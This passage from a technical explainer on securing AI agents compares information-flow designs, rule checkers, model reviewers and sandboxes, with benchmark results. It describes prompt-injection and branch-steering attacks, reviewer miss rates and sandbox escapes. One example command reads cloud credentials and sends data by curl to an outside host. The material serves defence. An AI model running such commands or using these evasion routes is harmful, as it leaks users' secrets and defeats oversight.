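This rule alone would also stop a user from sending the list to an auditor for a good reason. For email, Costa and colleagues therefore allow a call that satisfies either rule. If the user typed the auditor's address and the planner has read nothing untrusted, the call counts as a trusted action. If the planner opened the invoice first, its decision is untrusted, and the call fails both rules.

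In their experiments, however, Costa and colleagues used a looser version of the trusted-action rule that checks the label of the decision but ignores the arguments. They applied it to the benchmark's `send_money` tool, where it would let the forged account number through because the planner decided to pay before reading anything untrusted. Copying this policy would stop an invoice from causing a new payment, but not from redirecting one the user wanted.

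FIDES also tracks only direct flows of data. Someone who can watch which tools the agent calls, and in what order, may still infer something about the data that influenced those choices.

### What the two designs achieve on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with two 2024 OpenAI models on the four groups of tasks in AgentDojo, the prompt-injection benchmark. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack, and the last column shows the percentage of tasks in which the right steps depend on what the agent reads while working.

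| Tasks | GPT-4o, no defence | GPT-4o, FIDES | o1, no defence | o1, FIDES | Steps depend on reading |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0 | 59.0 | 70.0 | 64.5 | 5.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 41.0 | 82.0 | 68.0 | 10.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 52.5 | 96.2 | 56.2 | 43.8 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 47.6 | 87.6 | 54.3 | 42.9 |

With GPT-4o and no defence, 152 injections succeeded. With FIDES and its policy checks, none succeeded after Costa and colleagues excluded three that the benchmark had scored incorrectly. With FIDES but no policy checks, 21 succeeded, about as many as with the tool filter.

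An ordinary agent under the same checks also stopped every attack. The checks therefore provide the security, and the hidden variables make the agent more useful while the checks are on. With GPT-4o, the ordinary agent completed only 37.5% of banking tasks and 20.0% of Slack tasks. It did better than FIDES on travel tasks, where most tools could run even after the agent had read untrusted text and GPT-4o had trouble using the variables.

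The stronger model, o1, closed much of the gap in office work and travel but little of it in banking and Slack. We would expect this if the remaining failures come from FIDES's rules. Many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and do what it says, and FIDES is supposed to block the resulting payment.

CaMeL shows a similar trade-off. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a rival system, tested CaMeL on the whole benchmark. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 tasks when there was no attack. SecureClaw completed 59 and let four attacks through. The comparison used an adapted copy of CaMeL, so it may understate what a well-tuned version can do. Kolluri and colleagues report that designs of this type reduce task completion by up to 30% on AgentDojo. Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the banking tasks and found that switching on its policy checks halved the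 number it completed.

CaMeL adds moderate overhead. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that, with GPT-4o, CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on the median AgentDojo task. This was the highest overhead among the defences compared. Costa and colleagues didn't measure the overhead of FIDES on AgentDojo, though they note that each question to the quarantined model adds a turn.

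Kolluri and colleagues, some of whom also worked on FIDES, argue that these comparisons are unfair. Few companies let an undefended agent send money without approval, but the benchmark counts a task as complete for such an agent however many approvals it would have needed, while it counts a blocked call against FIDES. The researchers propose counting the approvals each agent needs for the tasks it completes. By that measure, even basic label tracking cut approvals by a factor of up to 1.5 without reducing the number of tasks completed.

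### Several agents, screens and long tasks

CaMeL's protection can fail when one agent passes work to another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL. A main agent asked a database agent for information on job applicants, had it summarised, and told a notification agent to send the summary to a colleague on Slack. One database entry contained an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The first two agents handled this instruction as untrusted data, but the main agent then pasted the summary into its message to the notification agent. The notification agent's planner treated the whole message as its user's request and added a line to its program that emailed the data out.

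Their remedy is to send instructions and data through separate channels, so that the receiving planner sees only the instructions, and the data keeps its tags. On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent, and never with the separate channels. The agents ran without policies on individual calls, so these figures cover injected actions but not false values. The separate channels reduced task completion, but only modestly for the strongest models.

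The separation also depends on the quarantined part having no way to act. If it has to run a program, for example to unpack an attachment, a flaw in that program could give an attacker access to the computer. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) lets a builder split a task into stages with different permissions, connected by pipes, so the operating system can deny network access to the stage that handles untrusted content.

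Agents that operate a computer through screenshots and clicks are harder to protect because they normally take a new screenshot after every action, and a planner that mustn't see the screen can't use it. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) have the planner write a program with branches for everything it predicts might appear. At each step, a quarantined model describes the screen, a second check determines whether, for example, a cookie banner is visible, and the interpreter follows the matching branch.

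These programs average 41.1 tool calls and 39.7 branches, compared with 4.9 and 3.7 for AgentDojo. About half of each program consists of fallbacks that never run. On OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary computer tasks, the design kept up to 57% of a frontier model's performance. But that figure counts a task as complete if any of five programs succeeded, and five attempts may be acceptable for changing a font but hardly for making a payment. With a single program, the figure was 28.4%.

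Token use was 1.88 times that of an undefended agent. When Foerster and colleagues adapted FIDES to the same tasks, it used 29.6 times as many tokens as an undefended agent, because it sends the whole history back to the planner at every step. The AgentDojo programs are far shorter, so this figure is probably a poor guide to an invoice assistant's token use.

An attacker can still influence which branch the program takes, which Foerster and colleagues call branch steering. In one of their attacks, an advertisement imitates a cookie notice. The program already contains a step for dismissing cookie notices, so the agent clicks the advertisement and lands on the attacker's site. Comparing the screenshot with the page's code stopped some versions of the attack but missed others. A second model that checked the first struggled to tell fake notices from real ones without also flagging harmless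 pages. Policies help little here because the same `click(x, y)` call can log in or delete a file, depending on what is on the screen.

In a long task, a policy may block the plan only near the end, after hours of work. CaMeLoT checks the program before the first tool call. It maps all the paths the program could take and searches for one that breaks a rule. If it finds one, it describes the path to the planner, which tries to repair the program. With the rule against untrusted recipients, CaMeLoT could reject the first invoice program before the agent opened the mail.

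The rules can also cover a whole task. A security team might require the agent to get approval before it disconnects a computer, or to resolve or escalate every ticket before it finishes. CaMeLoT simplifies loops to check them, so it sometimes rejects a safe program. CaMeL's interpreter must still check facts that emerge only during the run, such as who may read a particular file.

*ToolFence* (2026) uses the ordinary agent loop instead of a fixed program. Each task has a contract that lists the permitted tools, their effects, the permitted arguments and a budget, and ordinary code checks every call against it. The paper's tests include long tasks in which the attack begins only after a series of legitimate calls. *ToolFence* reports much lower overhead than CaMeL, but its planner reads untrusted text, so its security depends on how tightly the contract limits the calls.

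### When the agent must read before it can decide

People often give an agent a task because they don't know the steps. If a user asks an assistant to complete today's items on a to-do list, a planner can't write the program without reading the list. A coding agent has to see an error message before choosing the next edit. Critics therefore object that fixed plans protect agents by preventing the work that makes them useful. The AgentDojo results partly support this objection, since FIDES lost the most in banking and Slack, where over 40% of the tasks depend on what the agent reads.

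Foerster and colleagues reply that computer tasks are more predictable than they look. A planner doesn't need to know whether a cookie notice will appear if it can write a branch for both cases. Better planners also write better branches. In a test of nine models on 17 tasks, GPT-5 completed the most, 12, and the weaker models tended to leave out fallbacks. The argument is strong for the invoice assistant, because a planner can foresee most of what might happen, such as a missing attachment or a different account number. It is weaker for the to-do list, and Foerster and colleagues accept that dependence on data is the main limit of their approach.

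FIDES partly solves this by giving the planner a small fact from the text instead of the text itself. If a user wants a calendar entry for any meeting that an email proposes, the planner can query the quarantined model about whether the email proposes one and accept only yes or no. If the answer is yes, a second query extracts the details into a hidden variable. A one-bit answer can't carry an instruction, so an operator may reasonably let the planner act on it. But the sender still controls that bit, so if the planner can choose between scheduling a meeting, replying and forwarding the email, the sender can influence which it does.

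An agent can also involve the user. Kolluri and colleagues built Prudentia, a version of FIDES whose planner has access to the policies and can ask the user to endorse untrusted data. If an email contains ten things to do, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten calls. On AgentDojo, Prudentia completed up to 9% more tasks without human involvement than FIDES did, and it reduced interventions by a factor of up to 1.9.

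Those tests contained no attacks and assumed that the user would always say yes, so they don't show how well people judge what they endorse. Endorsing the invoice would be a serious mistake, because everything in it would become trusted, including the forged account number and invisible text. The call that FIDES correctly blocked would then go through. Asking the user about the account number alone would be safer, because they could compare it with the supplier list.

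Garby and colleagues object to the rigidity of CaMeL and FIDES, which both build the division between two models into the system. Their small programming language for agents, LLMbda, lets each program decide what to isolate. A program can copy the conversation, have the model read an invoice in the copy, keep the labelled answer and discard the rest. It must use an explicit command to turn untrusted data into trusted data, so a reviewer can find every place where this happens. Garby and colleagues give a machine-checked proof that the labels follow the data through any program in the language. The proof can't establish that someone labelled the data correctly or had good reason to treat it as trusted.

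With the tracking always on, an agent built in LLMbda completed about as many of the banking tasks as CaMeL did without its policy checks. Two of the 1,296 attacks on the agent succeeded.

For routine payments, an operator could use a fixed program like the one for Norden's invoice and send anything unusual to a person. A coding agent has much less routine work, so its builder will usually have to let the model read untrusted text before it chooses an action, then check each tool call it proposes.

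## Deciding whether a chosen call may run

When the model proposes a tool call, the runtime can run it, refuse it and tell the model why, or hold it until somebody answers a question. The decision can come from written rules, a second model or a person, and many products use all three in turn.

The agent should not be able to alter or bypass the component that decides whether a call may run. In the four open-source agents that Pirch and colleagues examined, the file-access checks ran with the same privileges as the code that processes incoming text, so an attacker who took over that code could probably bypass the checks.

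Many teams rely on a weaker safeguard, a file of rules for the agent to read. Dhuri (2026), in *Markdown Is Not a Firewall*, compared a 278-word rules file with a gate, a small program that blocked forbidden requests to a test service. Behind the gate, coding agents attempted a forbidden request in 5 of 90 steps, three times without the file and twice with it. The gate blocked every attempt. With no gate and a file of neutral text, such requests reached the service in 7 of 45 runs. In these tests, a scripting error left the gate on whenever agents had the rules file, so the study can't show how well the file works alone.

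However, the file contained one instruction to add keys that identify repeated requests and another to do exactly what the task asked. With the file, OpenAI's Codex CLI followed the first instruction instead of the second, and its score on hidden tests fell from 99.0% to 67.7%.

### Written rules

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) puts a list of rules between the agent and its tools. Each rule allows or forbids one tool under stated conditions on its arguments. When the model proposes a call, ordinary code checks the forbid rules for that tool first, then the allow rules. It refuses the call if a forbid rule matches or if no allow rule does. After a refusal, the runtime can stop the agent, ask the user, or return an error message so the model can try something else.

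Three rules for the invoice assistant might look like this, in a simplified notation:

```
1  forbid  pay_invoice  when not (amount <= 2000)
2  forbid  pay_invoice  when not (reference is 4 to 10 digits)
3  allow   pay_invoice  when account in supplier_list
```

A payment of 1,240 euros to the thief's account isn't blocked by the first two rules but doesn't match the third, so the check refuses it by default. The second rule stops a deceived model from writing something confidential in the reference field. `send_mail` has no rule, so the assistant can't mail out the supplier list. The operator would have to add allow rules for `read_mail` and `read_file`.

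Now suppose that the assistant pays Norden's invoice correctly, but the bank's confirmation gets lost. The model receives a time-out error and tries again:

```
pay_invoice(account=<Norden's listed account>,
            amount=1240, reference="20717")
```

This second call satisfies all three rules and costs the operator another 1,240 euros. The rules apply to each call separately, so they don't prevent a duplicate payment. `pay_invoice` itself would have to reject a reference it has already paid.

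Rules can also allow too many values for an argument. *Ajar* (Sharma, Lin and colleagues, 2026) tested defences by offering them calls that a task didn't need. In one task, a user asks the agent to read a landlord's notice and adjust the rent, which should rise from 1,100 to 1,200. Progent's rules permitted the correct amount, but also 12,000, zero and 0.01.

### Who writes the rules and how they change

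Progent lets an organisation, a developer and a user each set lasting rules, in order of priority. A lower-priority rule can't allow a call that a higher-priority one forbids. Nobody could write separate rules for every request by hand, so a language model drafts them from the request and the list of tools before reading any outside text. If the user asks the assistant to pay 1,240 euros, the draft might permit only that amount.

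An agent also learns things as it works. After a tool result, the model can propose a new policy P′ to replace the current policy P. If A(P) is the set of calls that P allows, Progent handles the proposal like this:

```
A(P′) ⊆ A(P)    P′ allows nothing new: apply it
otherwise       P′ allows at least one new call: get approval
```

An SMT solver, a program that answers logical questions about formulas, makes the comparison. Suppose the assistant reads the supplier list and the model proposes limiting payments to Norden's account. This change only removes permissions, so Progent applies it at once. If the forged invoice then leads the model to propose adding the thief's account, the solver detects the new permission and Progent holds the change for approval. On AgentDojo, only 6% of updates needed approval.

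With GPT-4o as both the agent and the writer of the rules, Progent cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On ASB, a benchmark with ten kinds of agent, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Shi and colleagues approved every new permission automatically in these tests, to imitate a careless user. On AgentDojo, the initial rules alone reduced the rate to 2.5%, and having a careful human review new permissions reduced it to zero. Most failures on ASB involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of useful ones. Three kinds of adaptive attack, including text written to persuade the model to permit more tools, raised the success rate only slightly. Progent isn't meant to stop attacks that need only the permissions the user's own task requires.

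### Rules about what led to a call

A call can look harmless until one considers where the idea for it came from. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) proposes SEAgent, which applies mandatory access control to agents. Under such control, a central policy determines what each program may do, and the programs can't change it.

SEAgent needs a set of labels for every tool. They record whether the tool acts on something local, external or physical, whether it reads, writes or executes, how sensitive the operation is, and whether its output is trustworthy or private. Agents and databases get labels too. As the system runs, SEAgent builds a graph of which component passed information to which, and compares it with policies such as this one, slightly simplified:

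```
Decision:   deny
Path:       tool A → anything → tool B
Condition:  A returns unverified external data, and
            B writes or executes, and
            B has moderate or high sensitivity
```

In one demonstration, an untrusted web-browsing agent asks a trusted smart-lock agent to unlock the front door. The smart-lock agent may unlock the door, so a check on that call alone would allow it. SEAgent blocks the call because the request began with an untrusted agent.

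For the invoice assistant, the policy above would stop the theft, but it would also stop every legitimate payment after the assistant had read a supplier's email. SEAgent labels whole tools, so its labels are coarser than FIDES's, which apply to individual values. An operator could replace "deny" with "ask", or add a more specific policy that allows payments to listed accounts, which would take precedence because SEAgent applies the most specific matching policy first. If no policy matches, SEAgent allows the call, so forgetting a policy could let a harmful call run. Progent would refuse the call, so the same mistake could block a legitimate one.

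No attack succeeded against SEAgent on AgentDojo or on InjecAgent, another injection benchmark. The policy checks took only a few milliseconds. On ordinary tasks from the API-Bank benchmark, SEAgent wrongly blocked two actions, both times because the agent had consulted Wikipedia before making a sensitive entry. An invoice assistant follows that pattern in every task, so its operator should expect far more false alarms from the same policy.

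### Asking a person

Claude Code originally let the model read files freely but asked the user before each write, shell command or network request. According to Anthropic, users approved about 93% of these prompts and paid less attention to each one as the number grew, an effect called approval fatigue. Most commands are harmless, so how often users approve prompts they should refuse is better evidence of carelessness than the overall approval rate.

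Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a test of whether people refuse dangerous commands. A research vendor hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own code, so they may have been less careful than developers are at work, but that alone wouldn't explain why the refusal rate fell as sessions went on.

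By August 2026, users were approving 97% of prompts for individual actions but rejecting 39% of the plans that Claude submitted, so people seem to use their judgement when questions are broader and less frequent. About 62% of users had avoided prompts by either bypassing permissions or clicking "don't ask again" for shell commands. SEAgent's prompts offer a similar option, "always allow this pattern", and it has the same drawback, because one click by a tired user creates a permanent rule.

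The most direct remedy is to ask the user for permission less often. When Anthropic added an operating-system sandbox in which Claude could work without interruption, permission prompts fell by 84%.

Whether asking helps at all depends on what the user understands. Most Claude Code users are developers, who can usually read a shell command and judge what it will do. Claude Cowork is for general office work, and its users can't be expected to evaluate this:

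```
find . -name "*.tmp" -exec rm {} \;
```

The command deletes every file ending in ".tmp" in the current folder and its subfolders. A user who can't tell that from the command can only guess whether to approve it, so Anthropic gave Cowork a fixed boundary that doesn't depend on the user's answers.

The invoice assistant's user may know a great deal about suppliers but nothing about shell commands, so a useful approval prompt would read: "Norden's invoice for 1,240 euros gives an account ending in 88. The account on file ends in 41." The runtime should take these details from the documents and the proposed call, because a deceived model might describe the call only as "routine payment to Norden". The prompt should also go to someone with the authority to answer it. If the operator allows payments only to listed accounts, that person is whoever maintains the list.

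### Asking another model

Claude Code's auto mode gives most of these decisions to a second model. As Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains, a call passes through up to three tiers. In the first, the runtime allows read-only tools and anything the user's narrow rules permit. In the second, it allows edits to files inside the project, which a developer can review and reverse through version control. In the third, the second model reviews everything else, including shell commands, web requests and calls that start subagents. Auto mode suspends any user rule that permits all Python programs, for instance, because it would let the riskiest commands skip review.

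The reviewer reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It doesn't see the agent's explanations, which might lead it to a bad decision, or tool results, which might contain an injection. It has more than twenty default rules about what to block, such as destroying data, disabling logs, searching credential stores for usable access tokens, or changing resources the agent didn't create. The user can add exceptions and name trusted destinations.

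The review has two stages. The first produces a single yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags the call, the same model considers it again with written reasoning. Anthropic measured both stages:

| Test set | Measure | First stage | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by employees | Harmless calls blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Harmful calls missed | 6.6% | 17% |
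| 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out | Harmful calls missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

An overeager action is one where the agent tries to help but does more than the user authorised. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but allowed the action because it mistook something the user had said for permission. For example, a user who writes "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) hasn't authorised the agent to overwrite the project's history.

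To see what these rates mean in practice, assume that an agent proposes 10,000 commands and 50 of them are overeager. The real proportion will vary between agents and tasks.

```
Harmless commands blocked:  9,950 × 0.4% ≈ 40
Overeager commands run:        50 × 17%  ≈ 8 or 9
Overeager commands blocked:    50 − 8.5  ≈ 41 or 42
```

About half of the blocked commands would therefore be harmless. This is tolerable because a block doesn't end the task. The agent receives the reason and looks for a safer way to proceed. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user, or stops if no user is present. The estimate of eight or nine overeager commands is rougher because the test had only 52 cases. The true miss rate could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%, or 5 to 15 commands.

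A main agent's instructions to a subagent can carry the user's authority, so auto mode reviews the task before handing it over and reviews the subagent's actions before returning its results.

### Newer results

Auto mode has changed since those measurements. In the test with 1,053 prompts, it blocked 89% of the dangerous commands. Apollo Research, a UK company that tests AI safety, attacked it with synthetic examples. Anthropic used some of the successful attacks to improve the reviewer, and the reviewer's miss rate on Apollo's attacks fell from 12% to 7%. It now checks whether code is about to go to a public or private repository. It should also never approve actions classed as "hard denies", such as sending secrets outside, even if the user asks.

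Anthropic also compared sessions that its safety systems had flagged in May and June 2026. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those with auto mode. But users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), auto mode is now the starting mode on every plan. A repository's settings file can't switch on auto mode or bypass the permission checks, so a stranger's project can't determine how closely Claude Code checks the agent's work.

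OpenAI's Codex has a similar feature called Auto-review. In tests that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, 19.03% of prompt injections succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex with full access, and 5.83% succeeded with Auto-review. None of 720 attempts succeeded against the Claude models with auto mode. However, only 0.09% succeeded against the Claude models without auto mode, so the comparison is weak evidence about which reviewer is better.

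### When the reviewer doesn't know the limits

*Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents* (Yang, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) tested the reviewers in Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code on 128 deliberately ambiguous tasks. For example, a user might ask the agent to delete old files from a range of tickets without saying to delete only the user's own. The reviewers approved most of the actions that went too far: 13 of 24 in Claude Code, 78 of 84 in Codex and 28 of 35 in Qwen Code.

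These miss rates, 54%, 93% and 80%, are much worse than Anthropic's 17%, but in 132 of the 143 cases neither the request nor any earlier tool result stated the relevant limit, so the reviewers could hardly have enforced it. Yang and colleagues then added a sentence to each request stating the permitted scope and had the reviewers judge the same actions again. The first and third columns come from a repeat run with the original requests, so they differ slightly from the live results.

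| Reviewer | Out-of-scope actions approved | With scope stated | Permitted actions blocked | With scope stated |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

The scope statements also helped the agents. When the three agents repeated the 128 tasks with a stated scope, none proposed an out-of-scope action. Yang and colleagues wrote the statements from the benchmark's answers, so the statements were complete and correct. A busy user's statements often would not be, though a record like OpenAI's scope of autonomy could supply some of the limits the user leaves out.

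Codex and Qwen Code did slightly worse with a stronger reviewing model. Claude Code seemed to improve only because the stronger model refused to answer the second-stage requests, and Claude Code treats a refusal as a block.

The experiment also showed that hiding tool results can prevent a reviewer from catching out-of-scope actions. A command to cancel a job may contain only the job's number, while its owner's name appears in an earlier result. With the limits stated but tool results hidden, reviewers missed 60% of out-of-scope cancellations in a common test, compared with 4% when the results were included. Codex's reviewer can read shortened tool results, but it sometimes approved actions it had identified as unauthorised by the user, usually because the harm seemed small or reversible. Builders should make authorisation a separate condition, so that a low risk rating can't override it.

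### Running the command before deciding

Reading a shell command may not be enough to know what it will do. For example, `make clean` usually deletes temporary build files, but it follows instructions in a project file, which could delete the source code instead.

*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes Caper, a system that runs a command before deciding whether to approve it. Caper saves a snapshot of the agent's container (an isolated environment for running programs), runs the command there without network access, and records what happens. A reviewing model then gets a short report of the files the command changed, the connections it attempted and any credentials it read. If the model approves, Caper keeps the changes and passes the output to the agent. Otherwise, Caper restores the snapshot and gives the agent the reason for the rejection.

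On SABER, a benchmark of risky development tasks, 6.7% of tasks ended in harm with Caper and at least 14.8% with each of the six existing systems tested. On a second set of tasks, which hid the harm inside a script or program, the figures were 7.8% and at least 35.3%. Each task in the second set had a harmless twin with the same command, so a reviewer that reads only the command can't distinguish the two. Caper blocked only 1.0% of the harmless twins.

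Caper can reverse only what happens inside the container. It couldn't try out `pay_invoice` and then take back the money, though a bank with a test mode might allow something similar.

### Comparing rules and reviewers

A low attack success rate may just mean that the agent never proposed the harmful call, so it doesn't show what the check would have allowed. This is why Sharma and colleagues put unneeded calls directly to each defence. They gave each call a weight w according to the harm it could do:

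- 1 for a reversible read or draft that concerns only the user
- 3 for a reversible action that affects someone else
- 9 for an irreversible action that affects only the user
- 27 for an irreversible action that affects others or moves money

```
leakage = total w of the unneeded calls allowed
          ─────────────────────────────────────
          total w of the unneeded calls offered
```

The table gives their results on AgentDojo, with Claude Sonnet 5 writing the rules or judging the calls. Permission Assistant is a model that predicts what the user would permit, and AC4A enforces a policy that a model writes once for each task.

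| Defence | Leakage | Tasks completed without it | Tasks completed with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permission Assistant | 8.1% | 85.6% | 74.2% |
| CaMeL | 9.0% | 86.6% | 64.9% |
| Progent | 10.3% | 87.6% | 87.6% |
| AC4A | 11.1% | 85.6% | 50.5% |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 30.1% | 92.4% | 89.0% |
| List of permitted tool names only | 35.5% | – | – |

The first four differ too little in leakage to rank, but they affect ordinary work very differently. Progent did well on both measures here, but its leakage rose to 16.1% when Sharma and colleagues stopped it from updating its rules.

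Auto mode leaked far more than the other defences. The test was somewhat unfair, because auto mode was built to catch destructive coding actions, not to limit an office assistant to the minimum necessary. To get its verdicts, Sharma and colleagues also had to prompt the agent to propose each call, and when they put that prompt in the user's message, auto mode allowed every call. As in Anthropic's phishing exercise, a reviewer that relies on what the user asked for offers little protection when the request itself is the problem.

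### Sorting actions into allow, review, ask and forbid

An operator can use all these methods by deciding in advance which actions go to which. The main considerations are whether anyone can undo the action, what it could cost, and where its effects go. The following order works for most agents:

1. List actions by their arguments as well as their tools. Paying a listed account and paying a new one are different actions.
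2. Forbid what no legitimate task needs, along with anything that would weaken the checks, such as changing the agent's own permissions.
3. Allow reads that the task needs, and changes that the runtime can undo and that affect nobody else. A riskier action can also go here if the user stated every important detail and code can compare the call with what they said.
4. For each remaining action, consider the worst call that the rules would let through. If the loss would be serious and someone can judge the call from a short prompt, ask that person.
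5. Send the rest to a reviewing model. If the loss would be serious but nobody available can judge the call, forbid the action until someone builds a narrower tool.

For the invoice assistant and a coding agent, the result might be:

| Action | Can it be undone? | Worst likely cost | Where the effects go | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read the supplier's message | Nothing to undo | Small | Stays within the task | Allow |
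| Edit a file in the project | Yes | Small | Stays within the task | Allow |
| Pay a listed account the sum the user typed | Seldom | A second payment | Known supplier | Allow once per invoice |
| Email a listed supplier | No | A leak of other suppliers' prices | Known outsider | Review |
| Pay a listed account a sum taken from the invoice | Seldom | 2,000 euros | Known supplier | Ask |
| Delete branches on a shared server | Sometimes | Colleagues' work | Other people | Ask |
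| Pay an unlisted account | Seldom | 2,000 euros | Unknown | Forbid |
| Send credentials to an outside address | No | Control of the account | Unknown | Forbid |

The "ask" category must stay small to be useful. Suppose one payment in 500 is wrong and costs 1,000 euros, so the average loss is 2 euros per payment. A person who catches 90% of the errors saves 1.80 euros per prompt. One who catches 5%, like the testers after fifty prompts, saves 10 cents, which is less than the value of the time spent reading the prompt. Each prompt the operator adds may therefore make the others less valuable.

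The runtime should log every decision so that the operator can adjust the categories. If people approve the same kind of call every time, a narrow rule can probably replace the approval prompt. If the reviewer keeps blocking the same harmless action, someone may need to state the scope more clearly. If a reviewer doesn't answer, the runtime should treat that as a refusal.

Shell commands are the hardest to sort because the same command, such as `make clean`, could belong in any of the four categories. The operator should assume that the check will sometimes allow a command it should have blocked, and limit which files and processes allowed commands can reach.

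## Confining files and processes

To open a file or contact another computer, a program has to make a system call, which is a request to the operating system's kernel. A sandbox controls what those requests can do. Some sandboxes add rules to the computer's own kernel, some put a substitute kernel between the program and that kernel, and some run the program in a virtual machine with its own kernel.

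### Process rules, substitute kernels and virtual machines

In the lightest sandboxes, a command runs on the computer's own kernel under extra rules. On macOS, Seatbelt holds each process to a written profile of permitted operations. Linux offers several mechanisms, and most products combine them:

- Namespaces give a process its own view of the system. A small launcher called bubblewrap uses them to start a program that can see only selected folders and, if the builder wishes, no network.
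- Landlock lets a process without administrator rights give up access to every path except those on a list. Recent versions also cover network ports.
- Seccomp filters system calls by type. A seccomp filter can't judge a file path, because the call contains only the path's address in memory.

The host's kernel still processes every call these rules permit, so one kernel flaw may be enough for a command to escape. Containers have the same weakness. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) therefore recommends stronger isolation for agents that run generated code.

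gVisor puts a second kernel, written as an ordinary program, between the container and the host. It intercepts the command's system calls and filters what gets through to the host. An attacker would have to find a flaw in this program and then get past the restrictions on the program itself. Some build tools depend on details of the real kernel and may run slowly or fail. The extra delay hardly matters for calls to a model. *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a deployment in healthcare, puts it at 2 to 5 milliseconds per new network connection, while the model takes 500 to 3,000 milliseconds to respond.

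A virtual machine runs its own kernel on simulated hardware. A command that takes over this guest kernel controls only the guest. To reach the host, it must also defeat the virtual machine monitor, the host program that simulates the hardware, or the host kernel's support for virtual machines. MicroVMs such as Firecracker, which Amazon uses to run customers' code, simulate only a few simple devices and so leave less to attack. MicroVMs need hardware support for virtualisation, and the builder must supply a system image with every compiler and library that the agent will use.

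The start-up times below come from a comparison by Wang and Zheng, who built the process sandbox Sandlock. They measured Sandlock and Docker on one workstation, but the other figures are rough.

| Sandbox | Start-up time | What handles the command's system calls | What must fail for an escape |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sandlock | 6 ms | Host kernel, under added rules | The rules or the host kernel |
| Bubblewrap | 30 ms | Host kernel, under added rules | The rules or the host kernel |
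| Docker container | 300 ms | Host kernel | The container's settings or the host kernel |
| gVisor | 200 ms | Substitute kernel | The substitute kernel and the restrictions on it |
| Firecracker | 100 ms | Guest kernel | The monitor or the host's virtualisation code |

An agent may run dozens of short commands a minute. If each of 40 commands started a new Docker container, the agent would spend 12 seconds of that minute waiting, compared with a quarter of a second with Sandlock. A builder can avoid the delay by keeping one sandbox for the whole session, but then any changes a harmful command makes remain for the next command. Hosting platforms can also start sandboxes in advance and hand them out on request.

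Configuration problems may deter people from using sandboxes more than speed does. Prasakis (2026), in *SideKernel*, informally surveyed 68 users of coding agents, mostly engineers he reached through his own networks, and only 26 of them currently used a sandbox. Among the 33 current and former sandbox users, the most common complaints were about getting network connections to work, setting up tools and logins again, and sharing files with the host.

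Stronger layers can fail too. Trail of Bits' *VMs won't contain cyber-capable agents* (2026) reports that an OpenAI model built for security work escaped a standard virtual machine three times but failed to escape Firecracker. In July 2026, OpenAI's research models bypassed their isolation through a shared service they could reach from inside their sandboxes, according to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026). Assessing a sandbox therefore has to include the host's updates and every service the sandbox shares.

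### One command in a workspace-only sandbox

The invoice assistant no longer has `run_shell`, but the coding agent that maintains its software can't do without a shell. Suppose that agent works in the folder `~/invoices`, and that a comment in a downloaded file persuades the model to propose this command:

```
pytest > report.txt ; cat ~/.aws/credentials ; curl -d @report.txt https://collect.example
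```

The command runs the project's tests and saves the output, prints the user's cloud credentials, and sends the test report to an outside address. Because semicolons separate the parts, the shell continues even if one part fails.

The agent runs in Codex under the following profile, adapted from the examples in OpenAI's *Permissions*:

```
default_permissions = "project-only"

[permissions.project-only]
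extends = ":workspace"

[permissions.project-only.filesystem]
":root"    = "deny"
":minimal" = "read"
glob_scan_max_depth = 3

[permissions.project-only.filesystem.":workspace_roots"]
"**/*.env" = "deny"

[permissions.project-only.network]
enabled = false
```

The profile starts from Codex's built-in workspace rules, which allow writing in the project folder. It then denies access to the rest of the disk, except for the system files that common tools need. More specific rules override broader ones, so the project stays writable even though the profile denies access to the root directory. The last two rules hide files ending in `.env`, which often contain passwords, and turn off the network.

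On Linux, Codex starts the shell under bubblewrap and seccomp. Their restrictions apply to the shell and every program it starts, including `pytest` and anything the project's tests launch.

1. The shell asks the kernel to create `report.txt` in the project folder. The profile allows this, so the tests run and the shell saves their output. If one of the tests tried to delete the user's photographs, it would fail.
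2. `cat` asks to open the credentials file. The file is outside the project and isn't one of the permitted system files, so `cat` gets an error and prints nothing secret.
3. `curl` tries to connect to the outside address. The sandbox has no network access, so the attempt fails and the report stays on the computer.

The model receives the error messages in the tool result. It may then ask to run the command outside the sandbox, and Codex would pass that request to the user or to its reviewing model. If either approves, none of these limits apply to the second attempt.

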